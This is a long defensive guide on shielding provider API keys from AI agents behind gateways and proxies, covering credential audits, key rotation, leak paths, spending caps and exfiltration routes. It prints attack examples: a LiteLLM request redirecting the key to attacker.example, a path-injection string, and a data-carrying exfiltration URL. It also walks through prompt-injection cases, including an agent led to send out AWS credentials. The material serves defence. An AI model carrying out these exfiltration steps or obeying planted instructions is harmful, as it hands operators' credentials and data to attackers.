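| How it receives the key | Environment variable | Standard input |
| Copy of the key on disk | Docker Compose file | None made by the proxy |
| Providers | Several, with a port for each | One |
| Access that would expose the key | Root on the host, or the Docker socket | Root on the host, or the Docker socket |

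A builder can run the gateway in its own container and give it the key through a file or standard input instead of an environment variable.

GitHub's agent container still has a `GITHUB_TOKEN`, which some tools need. To protect it, GitHub loads a library that replaces `getenv`, the standard function for reading an environment variable. The first call returns the token and removes the variable, and the library keeps a copy for later calls by the same program. This makes casual leaks less likely, but the `env` command doesn't use `getenv` and will print the token if it runs before the removal. According to *Authentication Architecture*, the token also disappears from `/proc/self/environ`. But Linux normally fills that file from the environment the process started with, and removing a variable doesn't erase it there, so an operator who relies on this protection should check the file in a running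 container.

The sidecar can also use workload identity federation to get a short-lived credential instead of storing an API key. It renews the credential when three quarters of its lifetime has passed. OpenAI's *Configuring workload identity federation for GitHub Actions* describes the same kind of federation for OpenAI's API.

### Finding the copies left behind

Adding a gateway leaves in place any keys already saved on the machine, and there may be many. *Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes a healthcare technology company that ran nine agents on separate virtual machines, using OpenClaw, an open-source agent framework, and Claude through Amazon Bedrock. An audit on 11 March 2026 found 12 credentials, including a GitHub token and Bedrock credentials, in one agent's `.bashrc`, the script that a shell runs at startup. A second agent had a Bedrock key in its own `.bashrc`. On two machines,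 every account could read `openclaw.json`, the file that stores all of an agent's credentials.

The company had already tried to fix this with its hardened machine image of 16 February, which restricted access to the `.env` files and the credential directory. The image didn't protect keys in `.bashrc`, and the audit 23 days later found them there. Controls also varied between machines, so a fix on one agent's machine could be missing from another's.

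The same day, the company deleted the `.bashrc` exports and set the readable files to mode 600. That mode couldn't keep the credentials from the agents, because each agent needed to read its own file. The company also saved backups of the `.bashrc` files, and a backup made before the deletion contains the keys. Maiti doesn't report that anyone replaced the keys. Stray `.env` files on two machines, at least one of which contained tokens, were still listed as unresolved.

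Six of the nine machines had no serious findings. The auditor, itself an AI agent, searched shell startup files, shell history, OpenClaw's settings, `.env` files and workspace files, so a clean result applies only to those places. The table below includes places it didn't search.

| Place | How a credential gets there | What to do |
|---|---|---|
| Environment variables | A shell profile or service definition exports them | Delete the export and restart every terminal and service that inherited it |
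| Dotfiles and project files | A person or a program saved the key in `.bashrc`, `.env` or a settings file | Delete it, including editor backups; earlier Git commits keep a copy |
| Mounted folders | The sandbox shares the developer's home directory | Mount only the project the agent is working on |
| Shell history | Someone typed the key in a command | Delete the entry from the history file |
| Logs and transcripts | A program printed its environment or recorded request headers | Delete old logs or move them where the agent can't read them |
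| Cloud metadata service | The cloud platform issues credentials to any program on the machine that asks | Block `169.254.169.254` from the sandbox |
| Docker socket | The operator mounted it so that the agent could build images | Remove it, or give the agent its own Docker service in a virtual machine |

Mounted folders need the most care. GitHub mounts the runner's whole disk read-only so that agents can use the compilers installed there, then covers selected paths with empty directories. According to its *Security Architecture*, the agent also has write access to the host's home directory and `/tmp`. Covering selected paths has the same drawback as listing forbidden headers, because a new tool's credential file remains visible until someone adds it to the list. Mounting a single project folder is safer if the operator can install the compilers in the sandbox.

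An agent that can reach the cloud metadata service may be able to get the key out of a secrets manager. On many cloud machines, the gateway logs in to the manager with the machine's identity, which it gets from the metadata address. An agent on the same machine can request the same identity and fetch the key. Blocking the address in the sandbox prevents this. On AWS, the operator can also require session tokens for metadata requests and limit the replies to one network hop, which normally keeps containers on Docker's default network from using the service.

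The healthcare company's planned network rules would let the audit agent contact Google's metadata endpoint. The agent also has SSH access to all nine machines, and Maiti calls it the highest-value target in the fleet. An ordinary scanning script could search the same files without following instructions planted in one of them.

The company planned to move its agents to Kubernetes, a system for running containers across many machines, and give each agent a credential sidecar. Maiti claims the sidecar eliminates this kind of exposure, but the audit covered the old machines, so it provides no evidence about the sidecar.

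In a Kubernetes build, the sidecar and the agent would share a pod, a group of containers that run together under one service account (the identity they use to call Kubernetes). If that account can read Kubernetes Secrets, where the company plans to store the keys, the agent can fetch them directly. The operator should deny the account that access and set `automountServiceAccountToken: false`, which keeps its token out of the containers. The company also plans to use gVisor, which puts a second kernel between a container and the host. Since gVisor normally runs a whole pod in one sandbox, it wouldn't separate the agent from the sidecar. A gateway in its own pod would be better isolated.

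### Replacing a key that has been in a sandbox

Copying a key leaves no trace on the machine, so if a key has ever been where an agent could read it, the operator can't be sure that nobody took it. The operator should replace the key even if the agent appears to have behaved well. Deleting the local copies doesn't affect a copy someone else has.

If there are signs of theft, such as unexplained charges or a key in a public log, the operator should revoke the key at once and accept that the agents will stop. Otherwise the following order avoids an interruption:

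1. Remove the old key from the places in the table above and confirm that new sandboxes start without it. Without this step, the same script or mount may expose the new key as well.
2. Create a new key at the provider for this gateway only, with the fewest permissions that work and a spending limit if the provider offers one.
3. Put the new key in the gateway's store from a terminal outside any sandbox. Restart the gateway if it reads the key only at startup, as OpenAI's Codex proxy does, or if it caches credentials, as Sandbox0's netd does.
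4. Send a request through the gateway, then check in the provider's console that the new key was the one used.
5. Revoke the old key at the provider.
6. Send a request with the old key from outside the sandbox. The provider should reject it.
7. Read the provider's usage records for the old key from the day it first entered a sandbox. An unfamiliar model, a burst of requests at night or a new address suggests that someone else had it.
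8. Destroy the old sandboxes, along with their snapshots, saved transcripts and backups.

People tend to postpone step 5 because an old script may still depend on the old key. The provider's usage records usually show whether anything still uses it.

Other secrets in the same files need the same treatment. In the healthcare case, someone who copied the model credentials from `.bashrc` could also have copied the GitHub token next to them. If the exposed key could create other keys, the operator should also list every key on the account, because the others may still work after the exposed key is revoked.

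### Why attackers target the gateway

A gateway can read every request and every answer. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (Xie, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes how someone who controls a gateway can collect every credential that passes through it. They can also change the model's answer before the agent sees it, for instance by replacing a package in an `npm install` command with a malicious one that has a similar name. The changed answer has the correct format, and the agent has no original to compare it with. An attacker can make the change only after a certain number of requests or when a keyword appears, so a short test finds nothing wrong.

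This has happened with routers, services that resell access to several model providers through one address. In *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026), Liu and colleagues tested 428 of them. Nine inserted malicious tool calls, two adapted their behaviour to avoid detection, and 18 abused credentials from the traffic they handled. The tests could have missed routers that attack only under particular conditions, so the true numbers may be higher.

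The study shows what an intruder could do in a company's own gateway, but it is a poor guide to how often such break-ins happen, because the operators of those routers chose to attack their customers. Xie and colleagues report that Liu and colleagues also tested client-side defences, including screening for unusual answers, and could evade each one. An agent that runs commands without asking is especially exposed. A sandbox limits the damage from a changed command, but the agent may still put malicious code in the project it is working on.

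An attacker can also reach a gateway through the software it is built from. LiteLLM is an open-source library and gateway that gives programs one interface to many model providers. In March 2026, two malicious versions, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8, appeared on PyPI, the public registry for Python packages, and collected credentials and cryptocurrency wallets. On a gateway, such code runs under the account allowed to read the keys, so file permissions and a separate account don't stop it. Anyone who installed either version should rebuild the machine from a clean image and replace every credential on it, since removing the package doesn't recover what it has already sent.

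According to OpenAI's incident report, agents the company was testing broke into outside systems in July 2026. A builder should therefore expect attacks on the gateway from the agent itself as well as from people who hijack the agent.

### Limiting the damage from a break-in

The gateway should contain as little code as possible. OpenAI's Codex proxy serves one path for one provider and has no user accounts or database. Xie and colleagues built a router called AEGIS in which only 851 lines of code handle the conversation, and it adds about six milliseconds per request. When they planted ten errors in it and asked two coding agents to review the code, one found eight and the other found all ten. The test was small, but few teams could review a large gateway with hundreds of dependencies. If an operator needs only one provider, a product that supports many adds code without any benefit.

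AEGIS runs those lines of code in an enclave, a region of memory that the processor protects even from the host's administrator. The client checks which code is in the enclave before it sends anything. When another company runs the gateway, this keeps its staff from reading or changing the conversation. It doesn't protect the provider key from them, because the host supplies that key to the enclave.

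The builder should also pin dependencies, which means fixing the exact version and checksum of every package. With a lock file made before March 2026, a rebuild of the gateway would not have installed either malicious LiteLLM version:

```shell
pip install --require-hashes -r requirements.txt
```

Pinning also keeps out security fixes until someone updates the file. Someone who had pinned version 1.82.7 on the day it appeared would have reinstalled the malicious code with every build. Waiting a few days before adopting a routine release gives others time to discover such code, but an urgent fix for a known flaw shouldn't wait.

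If a malicious package gets into the gateway, egress rules make it harder for the package to send keys out. A model gateway needs to contact its provider, its secrets manager if it has one, and little else. GitHub's sidecar sends its traffic through Squid, so code that collects keys there can't upload them to an unlisted server. The network has to block direct connections, because malicious code can ignore a proxy setting such as `HTTPS_PROXY`. An attacker could still send data out through their own account at the permitted provider.

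The gateway needs a separate interface for administration. Many gateways use one port for model requests and for commands that add providers, create tokens or change the upstream. The agent has to reach that port to work, so only the gateway's permission check stops it from running administrative commands. A privilege-escalation flaw in that check gives an ordinary user an administrator's powers, for example because the gateway verifies that a token is valid but not whose it is. The agent could then change the upstream to an attacker's server, and the gateway would send the key there. If the gateway accepts administrative commands only on a Unix socket that only the operator's account can open, the sandbox can't reach the faulty check. A separate interface wouldn't have stopped a LiteLLM flaw that let callers choose the destination in an ordinary request (see "Keeping the key out of what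 the agent gets back").

The gateway's records need protection too. OpenAI's Codex proxy can save each request and response to a directory for debugging. It hides the `Authorization` header and cookies but saves everything else, including the conversation and any key the agent sent in another header. At a healthcare company, those files could contain patients' data. An operator who needs records only for billing and investigation can log the time, sandbox, model, token count and status without the conversation.

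Finally, each gateway should have its own key. GitHub's sidecar can hold keys for OpenAI, Anthropic, Copilot and Gemini in one container, and a flaw in any of its handlers could expose them all. A job that uses only Claude should give the sidecar only the Anthropic key. OpenAI recommends a dedicated project for each application or workload and lets an administrator restrict a key's permissions, so a gateway that only forwards requests to the Responses API can use a key with only the `api.responses.write` permission. If someone steals a gateway's key, the provider's records show which gateway it came from, and revoking it stops only the agents behind that gateway.

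## Keeping the key out of what the agent gets back

The gateway sends the provider key out with every request and passes the reply to the agent. If the reply contains the key, the agent has it, even if the operator removed every copy from the sandbox. A reply can also contain a different credential that works in its place, such as a temporary token. Someone who controls the agent can look for requests that produce such replies, but several of these leaks can happen by accident.

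### Servers that repeat the request

Some web services send back the headers they receive so that developers can see what their software is sending. If a proxy adds a key to a request to one of these services, the agent gets the key in the reply. Infisical, which makes a secrets manager, uses this to show new users that its proxy works. In the setup test in its *Agent Proxy Quickstart*, `curl` runs where the agent would run and gets a test key back in full.

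The proxy works correctly in that test, because the operator has assigned the key to that host. The large model providers' APIs don't normally repeat request headers in their responses, but a company's own model server, or a second gateway between the first one and the provider, may have a debugging page that does.

To prevent this leak, the operator should limit each key to an exact host that doesn't return request headers in its responses, and to as few paths as possible. A gateway with one fixed upstream and a short list of inference paths already does this. A proxy that covers many services needs more care, because a wildcard rule such as `*.example.com` also allows the key to reach any forgotten test server in that domain. When a host has no rule, Infisical forwards the request without a credential or, in a stricter mode, rejects it with a 403 error.

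OpenShell's attached providers were less strict than this in May 2026. A provider profile lists hosts, but according to NVIDIA the list didn't yet restrict which requests could receive the credential. The placeholder for a model key might therefore also be replaced with the real key in a request to another host the sandbox is allowed to contact. If that host repeated the request headers in its response, the agent would get the key. Anyone using a later release should check whether NVIDIA has changed this before adding a host that repeats headers to the policy.

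### Error messages that quote the key

A server that rejects a credential sometimes quotes it in the error message. *Using Secrets in Agents*, from the documentation for the agent runtime Scarab, gives the example of a reply that reads "Error: invalid token" followed by the token, which Scarab blanks out.

A key that the provider rejects as invalid is usually useless to a thief, but a malformed header can expose a key that works. Suppose the gateway is written in Python and its key file ends with a stray line break. If the gateway puts the file's contents in a header without trimming them, Python's standard HTTP library raises an error instead of sending the header. The error message is `Invalid header value` followed by the value, which includes the whole key. If the gateway returns the text of its own errors, which is convenient during development, the agent gets the key.

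The gateway should answer every internal failure with a fixed message and a reference number that the operator can look up. For a 401 or 403 error from the provider, it can keep the status code and replace the text, since the agent can't fix the key. It has to pass on some other errors, such as one for a conversation that is too long, because the agent needs them to correct its request.

Some services quote only part of a key in their error messages. If a key has 40 random letters and digits and an error shows the last four, the other 36 are impossible to guess in practice. But a second message may show a different part of the key, which leaves fewer characters to guess.

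### Redirects and destinations the caller can choose

A redirect is a reply that tells the client to try another address, and many HTTP libraries follow redirects automatically. When a redirect leads to a different host, both `curl` and Python's Requests library drop the `Authorization` header, which carries OpenAI keys, but they keep most custom headers. Anthropic's `x-api-key` is a custom header, so a gateway built on either could send an Anthropic key to a stranger's server.

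A provider has little reason to redirect a model request, so the gateway should not follow redirects. It can return an error and log the redirect address. Passing the redirect to the agent usually doesn't expose the key, because the agent then makes a new request and the proxy checks the new host against its rules. But the address itself can be sensitive, such as a signed download link that works for anyone who has it.

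In 2024, LiteLLM, the open-source gateway described in the previous section, had a flaw that let the caller name the destination outright. Airia's *Your AI Gateway Is a Skeleton Key* (2026) describes it under its number in the public catalogue of software flaws, CVE-2024-6587. A caller could add a field named `api_base` to an ordinary model request:

```json
{"model": "<model-id>",
 "api_base": "https://attacker.example",
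 "messages": [ ... ]}
```

LiteLLM then sent the request to that address with the provider key in the `Authorization` header. The attacker only needed to be able to make a model call, which every agent behind a gateway can do. A commercial gateway with the same field would have the same problem, although Airia, which sells AI management software, uses LiteLLM's record to argue for buying from a commercial vendor.

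The field makes sense when a program uses LiteLLM as a library, because the caller owns the key and may send it anywhere. In a gateway, the caller doesn't own the key, so the gateway has to take the upstream address from its own configuration and reject any request field that names a server.

A caller may also be able to change the destination through the path. Suppose a gateway builds the upstream address by joining `https://api.anthropic.com` to whatever path the agent sends. If the agent sends `.attacker.example/v1/messages`, the result is `https://api.anthropic.com.attacker.example/v1/messages`, which points to a server in the attacker's domain. To guard against this, the credential proxy in Varlock, a tool for managing secrets, rejects a request inside a tunnel unless its path begins with a slash, according to Varlock's *Proxy routing rules*.

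The gateway's configuration needs the same protection, because whoever writes it decides where the key goes. Solace's *Secrets and Variables*, the documentation for an agent platform, warns that anyone who can publish a skill to an agent chooses both the credentials it uses and the endpoints it contacts. Solace does not try to restrict these choices field by field, so an operator who lets an agent install skills on such a platform in effect lets the people who wrote them decide where the keys go. Infisical's *Proxied Services* describes a useful safeguard. Only people who already have permission to read a secret can create or edit a proxy rule that uses it, so nobody can obtain a key they aren't allowed to see by editing the rules.

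### Provider endpoints that issue credentials

A request to the real provider can also return a new credential. In OpenAI's Realtime API, which handles live speech, `POST /v1/realtime/client_secrets` accepts an ordinary API key and returns a short-lived one. A website's server uses this endpoint to give a visitor's browser direct access to the model without revealing the main key. An agent that could call it through the gateway would get a credential that works outside the sandbox, and could request another when that one expired.

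OpenAI and Anthropic also have administrative APIs that list an organisation's keys. These APIs require a separate admin key and show only part of each listed key. OpenAI's can also create a service account and return the account's new key in full. A gateway for model calls should never hold an admin key, and the operator should read the provider's current API reference before permitting any path that isn't plainly for inference.

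When the gateway uses workload identity, it should call Anthropic's token endpoint, `/v1/oauth/token`, over its own connection and keep the reply from the agent. If the gateway forwarded the agent's calls to that path and added its own identity token, the agent would receive the access token.

Infisical's proxy can also create short-lived credentials on demand. An agent whose own identity has permission to create them could do so without the proxy. To prevent this, Infisical refuses by default to start such an agent when the proxy runs on a separate machine, according to its *Proxied services*.

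Signing requests doesn't remove this danger. Varlock has a plugin that re-signs requests to Amazon's cloud with the real keys, and its sample rule covers `*.amazonaws.com`. That pattern includes Amazon's Security Token Service, which can return temporary keys in response to a single signed call. The sample also limits what the plugin will sign with the line `allowedServices=[bedrock, s3]`, and a builder who copies the sample should keep that line.

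The gateway also has to check the path that the provider will act on. If it allows every path that begins with `/v1/responses`, the agent can request `/v1/responses/../realtime/client_secrets`, which a server that resolves the `..` would treat as a request for a client secret. Varlock resolves such paths before comparing them with its rules, and sends the resolved version upstream. It rejects paths that different servers might interpret differently, such as one with an encoded slash. A gateway that accepts only exact paths avoids most of the problem.

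Revoking the provider key may not cancel temporary credentials already created with it. After such a leak, the operator should check how long those credentials last and whether the provider can cancel them separately.

### Gateway logs and debugging pages

An agent can also find the key in the gateway's log. A developer whose model calls are failing may well give the log to a coding agent to diagnose. The log may also be in a folder that the sandbox mounts, or on a status page served from the port the agent uses for model requests.

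Masking a key helps only if it hides the secret part. In CVE-2024-9606, another LiteLLM flaw that Airia lists, the log masked only the first five characters of a key. Anthropic's keys begin with `sk-ant-`, so an attacker would already know those five characters.

Logs can also contain gateway tokens. LiteLLM reports that it failed to remove request headers from some of the data it logged. This happened only if the operator had added a custom guardrail (a check on requests or replies) that returned the whole request. Anyone who could read those logs might have been able to use another caller's token.

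A key can also be in the path of a request. Telegram's bot API, for example, takes the bot's token there. Infisical records the path of every request in its session logs. A proxy that adds a secret to the path has to log the path as the agent sent it, so the secret stays out of the logs.

The gateway can also keep the key out of its log by recording each request before adding the key. It can log later events, such as the replacement of a token, by name and time only. NVIDIA does this in OpenShell, whose logs show when a credential expires and when the next one is due, but not the credential itself. Debugging pages belong on the separate administrative interface.

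### Where the proxy swaps the placeholder

A gateway for model calls can overwrite whatever the agent put in the authentication header with the real key. Some services expect the credential in the URL or the body, so some proxies instead search the request for a placeholder and replace it with the real key. Because the agent writes the request, it can choose where these proxies insert the key.

If the coding agent runs `env` while it works on the failing test, every later request contains the placeholder in both the header and the body. A proxy that replaces the placeholder in both places sends Claude the real key as part of the conversation. If Claude then copies that key into a configuration file it writes, the real key enters the sandbox in Claude's reply. This can happen without an attacker, and Varlock describes agents quoting their own environment variables in this way as routine.

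If the proxy swaps placeholders in request bodies, an attacker can get the key faster by having the agent ask the model to repeat the placeholder. In Varlock's example, the agent sends an email with the placeholder in its text, and the proxy replaces it with the real secret on the way to the mail service. OpenAI's and Anthropic's APIs both let a request name a remote MCP server and a token for the provider to send there. The agent can give an attacker's server address and use the placeholder as the token. The proxy then inserts the real key, and the provider sends it to the attacker.

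According to NVIDIA's *Manage Providers and Credentials*, OpenShell's proxy originally replaced credential placeholders in header values, query strings and paths, but didn't change request bodies, cookies or responses. If it found a placeholder it couldn't resolve, it rejected the request with an HTTP 500 error. The newer documentation includes a setting called `request_body_credential_rewrite`, which is `false` in NVIDIA's sample profile. Operators should check that it is `false` for every model provider.

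Docker's experimental custom secrets now swap placeholders only in headers. For older installations, which follow Docker's *Credentials*, it is safer to assume that the proxy also swaps placeholders in bodies.

Infisical's Agent Proxy lets the operator choose, for each secret, whether to substitute it in the path, query, header, body or any combination of these. According to the earlier edition of its documentation, the proxy replaces every occurrence of the placeholder in the selected parts, including bodies of up to 10 MiB, but forwards compressed bodies unchanged. Infisical has since deprecated Agent Proxy in favour of Agent Vault, which it describes as substituting the credential "where the agent sent a placeholder". That wording doesn't rule out bodies. Someone setting up Infisical for a model API should choose the header option.

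Varlock can insert secrets into request bodies with less risk. By default, it swaps placeholders only in headers, except those that servers often log or forward, such as `User-Agent` and `Referer`. To use a secret in a body, the operator has to name the field, for example `body:client_secret`. The proxy makes one swap in each place the operator has named and blocks the request if the placeholder occurs there twice, because it can't determine which copy is the real use. If the placeholder appears in a part of the request the rule doesn't cover, the proxy forwards it unchanged and records this in its audit log. Blocking those requests would stop an agent from working as soon as it had run `env`. Varlock's `body:*` setting allows the swap anywhere in a body, which would bring back the problem with the failing test if used with a model API.

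### Scanning replies for the key

A gateway has the key it sends, so it can search each reply for that key and remove it. Varlock's proxy does this, but *Credential proxy* lists limitations: the proxy scans only uncompressed text of up to 2 MB, and it looks only for exact copies. An agent can set the `Accept-Encoding` header to request a compressed reply, which the proxy will pass on without scanning. These limitations contradict Varlock's *Docker Sandboxes*, which claims that with scanning, an endpoint that repeats a header "cannot hand the real secret back to the agent". Varlock advises users to assume that an agent can recover the secret from any host that returns it.

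The gateway can avoid the compression problem by replacing the agent's `Accept-Encoding` header with one that requests uncompressed replies. Streaming is harder to handle because a key can be split across chunks. Suppose one chunk ends with the first 25 characters of a 40-character key, and the next begins with the other 15. A scanner that searches each chunk separately won't find the key, but the agent will have all of it after joining the chunks.

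The scanner therefore has to keep the end of each chunk and search it together with the next one. It needs to keep 39 characters, because that is the most of a 40-character key that can arrive without completing it. It must also hold those characters back. If it had already forwarded them, it would recognise the key only after the agent had received the first 25 characters. This Python function does both:

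```python
def scrub(chunks, key):
    keep = len(key) - 1              # 39 for a 40-character key
    held = ""
    for chunk in chunks:
        text = (held + chunk).replace(key, "[removed]")
        held = text[-keep:]          # wait for the next chunk
        yield text[:-keep]           # safe to send now
    yield held
```

In the example, `held` contains 14 characters of ordinary text and the first 25 characters of the key. When the second chunk arrives, the function finds all 40 characters of the key together and removes them.

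The function works when the key is in one continuous piece of text, such as a repeated header. It fails when a model writes the key out, because providers stream the answer as a series of small JSON messages, each with a few characters of text, which leaves JSON between the pieces of the key. The scanner has to extract the text from each message before joining it. Waterwall's *Reversible-tokenization egress proxy for AI coding agents* describes a proxy that has to find its own placeholders in streamed answers. The proxy waits for each block to finish before processing it, which is simpler but means the user no longer sees the text appear gradually.

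A filter that searches for anything that looks like a key, instead of one known value, can miss part of a key that is split across chunks. If it redacts the first part and then searches the redacted text, the marker `sk-***` no longer matches the pattern, and the rest of the key gets through. TYPO3, a content management system, documents a design that avoids this by holding back 128 bytes and searching the original text again each time a chunk arrives.

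Even a scanner that joins everything correctly misses an encoded copy. In Base64, a common way of writing data as plain letters and digits, a 40-character key becomes 56 characters, and `sk-ant` becomes `c2stYW50`. A search for the original key misses this copy, which the agent can decode with one command. The scanner could look for the Base64 form too, and Varlock does so for one kind of login header that its own proxy encodes. But a server can also escape the key, shorten it or write it in hexadecimal. If the model has received the key, an attacker can ask it to write the key with spaces between the characters.

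Scanning can also damage good replies. wardn, another credential proxy, ignores secrets of eight characters or fewer, presumably because short strings also occur in ordinary text. API keys are long enough that this rarely matters.

### Which rules to rely on

The rules that prevent exposure determine where the key goes and what the gateway itself returns or records. They still work if an attacker controls the agent, because nothing in the agent's request can change them.

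| How the key gets back | Sign that it has happened | Rule that prevents it |
|---|---|---|
| A server repeats the headers | A reply contains `authorization` or `x-api-key` with a value the agent didn't send | Assign the key only to hosts and paths that don't repeat headers |
| An error message quotes the key | The gateway returns a 500 error for a request that the provider has no record of | Return fixed error messages |
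| The gateway follows a redirect | The gateway connects to a host outside its configuration | Don't follow redirects |
| The caller names the destination | The gateway connects to an address that appears in the agent's request | Take the upstream only from the configuration |
| The provider issues a new credential | Someone uses the account from another address or after the sandbox has stopped | Permit only exact inference paths, and keep admin keys out of the gateway |
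| The agent reads a log or debugging page | The agent's transcript contains lines from the gateway's log | Record requests before adding the key, and serve debugging pages elsewhere |
| The proxy swaps a placeholder in the body | A reply contains the real key where the agent wrote the placeholder | Overwrite the header instead of searching for a placeholder |

Scanning and log masking only catch mistakes. A scanner is worth having on a gateway that serves many upstreams, because someone may later add a host with a debugging page. On a gateway with one provider and a few permitted paths, a scanner adds code that has to parse every reply to catch a leak that the other rules already prevent. If a scanner finds a key, the operator should replace it and look for the rule that failed, because the scanner may have missed a copy in an earlier reply.

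When an upstream has to receive a secret and can't be trusted not to repeat it, the only option left is to use a service that accepts signed requests instead. With Amazon's SigV4, a server that repeats the request headers returns only a signature, which is valid briefly and only for that request.

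## Limiting what an agent can do through the gateway

A hijacked agent that can't obtain the provider key can still use it through the gateway. If a planted instruction makes the coding agent send the model ten thousand requests, the gateway adds the key to each one and the provider bills the operator for them.

### Why the gateway can't tell a hijacked agent from a working one

Norm Hardy described the confused deputy in 1988 with the example of a compiler that had permission to write in the directory where a computer company kept its billing file. A user without that permission named the billing file as the destination for the compiler's debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the file. Dantuluri and Sundi (2026), in *Delegation Without Trust*, apply Hardy's idea to AI agents. In their version, an attacker plants text that leads an agent to use authority it has for a purpose its owner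 didn't intend.

With a gateway, this can happen twice. The README misleads the agent, and the agent's request then misleads the gateway. Hardy's remedy was to make each caller present its own authority for each file it names, so that the user's request would have failed. It doesn't help much here, because the developer's request and the attacker's come from the same agent, with the same credential, path and headers. A gateway also can't reliably tell from the text of a prompt who wanted it sent.

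The model can't always judge either. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal test in February 2026 in which a researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prompt into Claude Code. The prompt included ordinary setup steps, but it also asked Claude to read the employee's AWS credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Claude Opus 4.7 gave in to only about 0.1 per cent of single attempts on a prompt injection benchmark, but in the February test the instruction came from the user, so Claude had little reason to distrust it.

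The gateway's limits therefore have to be ones the operator can accept even if an attacker writes every request.

### How much a hijacked agent can spend

Anthropic's *Pricing* lists Claude Opus 5.5 at $4 per million input tokens and $20 per million output tokens. A token is a short piece of text, often part of a word. Suppose the model writes 80 tokens a second and an attacker keeps one answer running all day:

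80 tokens × 86,400 seconds = 6,912,000 tokens
6.912 million tokens × $20 = $138.24

Generating fifty answers at once costs $6,912 a day. The attacker can raise this to about $34,560 by requesting fast mode, which could generate text up to 2.5 times as fast at twice the price per token. A gateway that fixes only the model name doesn't prevent this, because fast mode is a separate option on the same model.

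The gateway needs to limit input as well as output, because input also costs money. Opus 5.5 accepts prompts of up to a million tokens, and a 900,000-token prompt costs $3.60 before any output. Sending one such prompt a minute costs $5,184 a day. At roughly four bytes per token, the prompt is about 3.6 MB, so the 10 MB limit in GitHub's sidecar would let it through.

Each kind of limit leaves a gap that another has to cover:

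| Limit | What it prevents | What can still happen |
|---|---|---|
| Requests per minute | A fast loop of small requests | A few very large requests |
| Simultaneous requests | Fifty streams at once | One stream running all day |
| Request size and `max_tokens` (the longest answer a request allows) | A single very expensive request | Many ordinary requests |
| Permitted models and options | A higher price per token | Heavy use of the permitted model |
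| Money per day | A total above the cap | The attacker uses up the cap, and the agent stops working |

The daily cap matters most because it limits the loss directly. The others slow the spending down, which gives someone time to notice.

### Setting the cap from expected use

Anthropic's example of a one-hour coding session with Opus 5.5 uses 50,000 input tokens and 15,000 output tokens, which cost $0.50. Eight such hours cost $4. A busy agent probably costs more, because it sends the whole conversation again with every request. Forty requests that average 30,000 tokens each use 1.2 million input tokens, which cost $4.80.

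With prompt caching, the provider charges much less for text it has recently processed. Cached input for Opus 5.5 costs $0.20 per million tokens, so those 1.2 million tokens would cost about $0.24 if nearly all of them came from the cache. A change in the agent's software that stops caching from working could therefore make its input cost 20 times as much, even without an attack.

A cap of $20 a day for each sandbox is a reasonable start, since it is five times the eight-hour estimate. One stream at $138 a day would reach it in about three and a half hours, and fifty streams in about four minutes. After two weeks, the operator can reset the cap to two or three times the cost of the busiest normal day. An alert at half the cap gives someone time to investigate before the agent stops.

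The gateway has to enforce the cap before it forwards a request. If it only adds up the cost of finished requests, fifty requests that arrive together when the total is $19 will all pass. With `max_tokens` at 64,000, their answers could cost another $64. To prevent this, the gateway can reserve the most that each request could cost:

reserved amount = input tokens × input price + `max_tokens` × output price

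For a request with 30,000 input tokens and a `max_tokens` of 8,000, the gateway reserves $0.12 for input and $0.16 for output, or $0.28 in total. When the reply ends, the gateway reads the actual token counts from it and releases the unspent amount. If the agent disconnects before the counts arrive, the gateway should keep the whole amount reserved, or an attacker could avoid the spending cap by disconnecting early.

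The gateway's token estimate needs a margin. According to an earlier edition of the price list, Anthropic's newer models split the same text into about 30 per cent more tokens than its older ones. Some request options also change the price. Writing to the one-hour cache costs twice the normal input price, and restricting processing to the United States adds 10 per cent.

A spending limit at the provider is a useful backup in case the gateway miscounts. But it applies to everything that shares the key or the account, so one hijacked agent could use up the limit and stop all the others.

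### Data that leaves in an ordinary prompt

An agent has to send data to the provider with every prompt. When the coding agent asks about a failing test, the test output and often the surrounding source code leave the company. Egress rules can't block this data without also cutting the agent off from its model.

The risk with prompts is that the agent sends the provider something the company has promised not to share. A prompt alone doesn't normally give an attacker the data, because it goes to the operator's account. A gateway could search prompts for customer names or secrets, but a hijacked agent can encode them first. Keeping files that contain them out of the sandbox is more reliable.

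### Web requests made by the provider

A prompt can carry data to an attacker if it makes the provider contact another server. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, a program can turn on web fetching by naming the tool in a model request. Anthropic's servers then retrieve pages, so the sandbox's egress rules don't apply. The same is true of OpenAI's web search.

The agent can also use the tool to send data out, because a web address can contain data. Suppose an attacker owns `attacker.example` and wants a file from the project. The agent puts part of the file in the address:

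```
https://attacker.example/?part=1&data=c2VjcmV0...
```

When Anthropic's server requests this page, the attacker's server records the address, which the attacker then decodes. Anthropic warned in an earlier edition of the page that website publishers may keep any parameters in the address.

Anthropic restricts the fetch tool to addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, so Claude can't make one up. This helps in a chat product, where a person writes the messages. It is much weaker behind a gateway, because a script in the sandbox can write the whole conversation, including the messages supposedly from the user. Even without such a script, the output of the agent's tools counts as part of the conversation. A planted instruction could have the agent run a shell command that prints an address, and by Anthropic's published rules the tool could then fetch it.

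The tool accepts addresses of up to 250 characters. If 200 of those carry data, sending a 10 kB file encoded in Base64 takes 67 fetches. Anthropic sets no default limit on the number of fetches and charges only for the tokens in the pages. A fetched page can also contain new instructions, so the attacker can direct the agent while it works.

Anthropic suggests turning the tool off, limiting the number of fetches with `max_uses`, or limiting the sites with `allowed_domains`. These are all set in the request, which the agent writes, so they protect the operator only if the gateway adds them or rejects requests without them.

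Anthropic's sample request turns the tool on in the body and has no `anthropic-beta` header, so blocking that header wouldn't stop it. The gateway has to read the `tools` list in the body and reject tools that run at the provider, including web search, code execution and remote MCP servers. It should also reject images and documents given as URLs, because the provider fetches those too.

If an agent needs the web for its work, the gateway can write its own `allowed_domains` list into each request. A listed domain includes all its subdomains, so an operator shouldn't list a domain where anyone can publish a page, such as `github.io`. The names should also use only ordinary Latin letters, because a name with a Cyrillic "а" in place of the Latin "a" looks the same but is a different domain.

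### Uploading files with the attacker's key

In October 2025, a security researcher showed that an attacker could take files through Anthropic's own API. At the time, Claude's code sandbox could by default contact only a short list of addresses, mainly for installing packages. The list also included `api.anthropic.com`. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes the attack:

1. The attacker hid instructions in a document, and the victim asked Claude to summarise it.
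2. Claude copied text from the victim's last conversation into a file in the sandbox.
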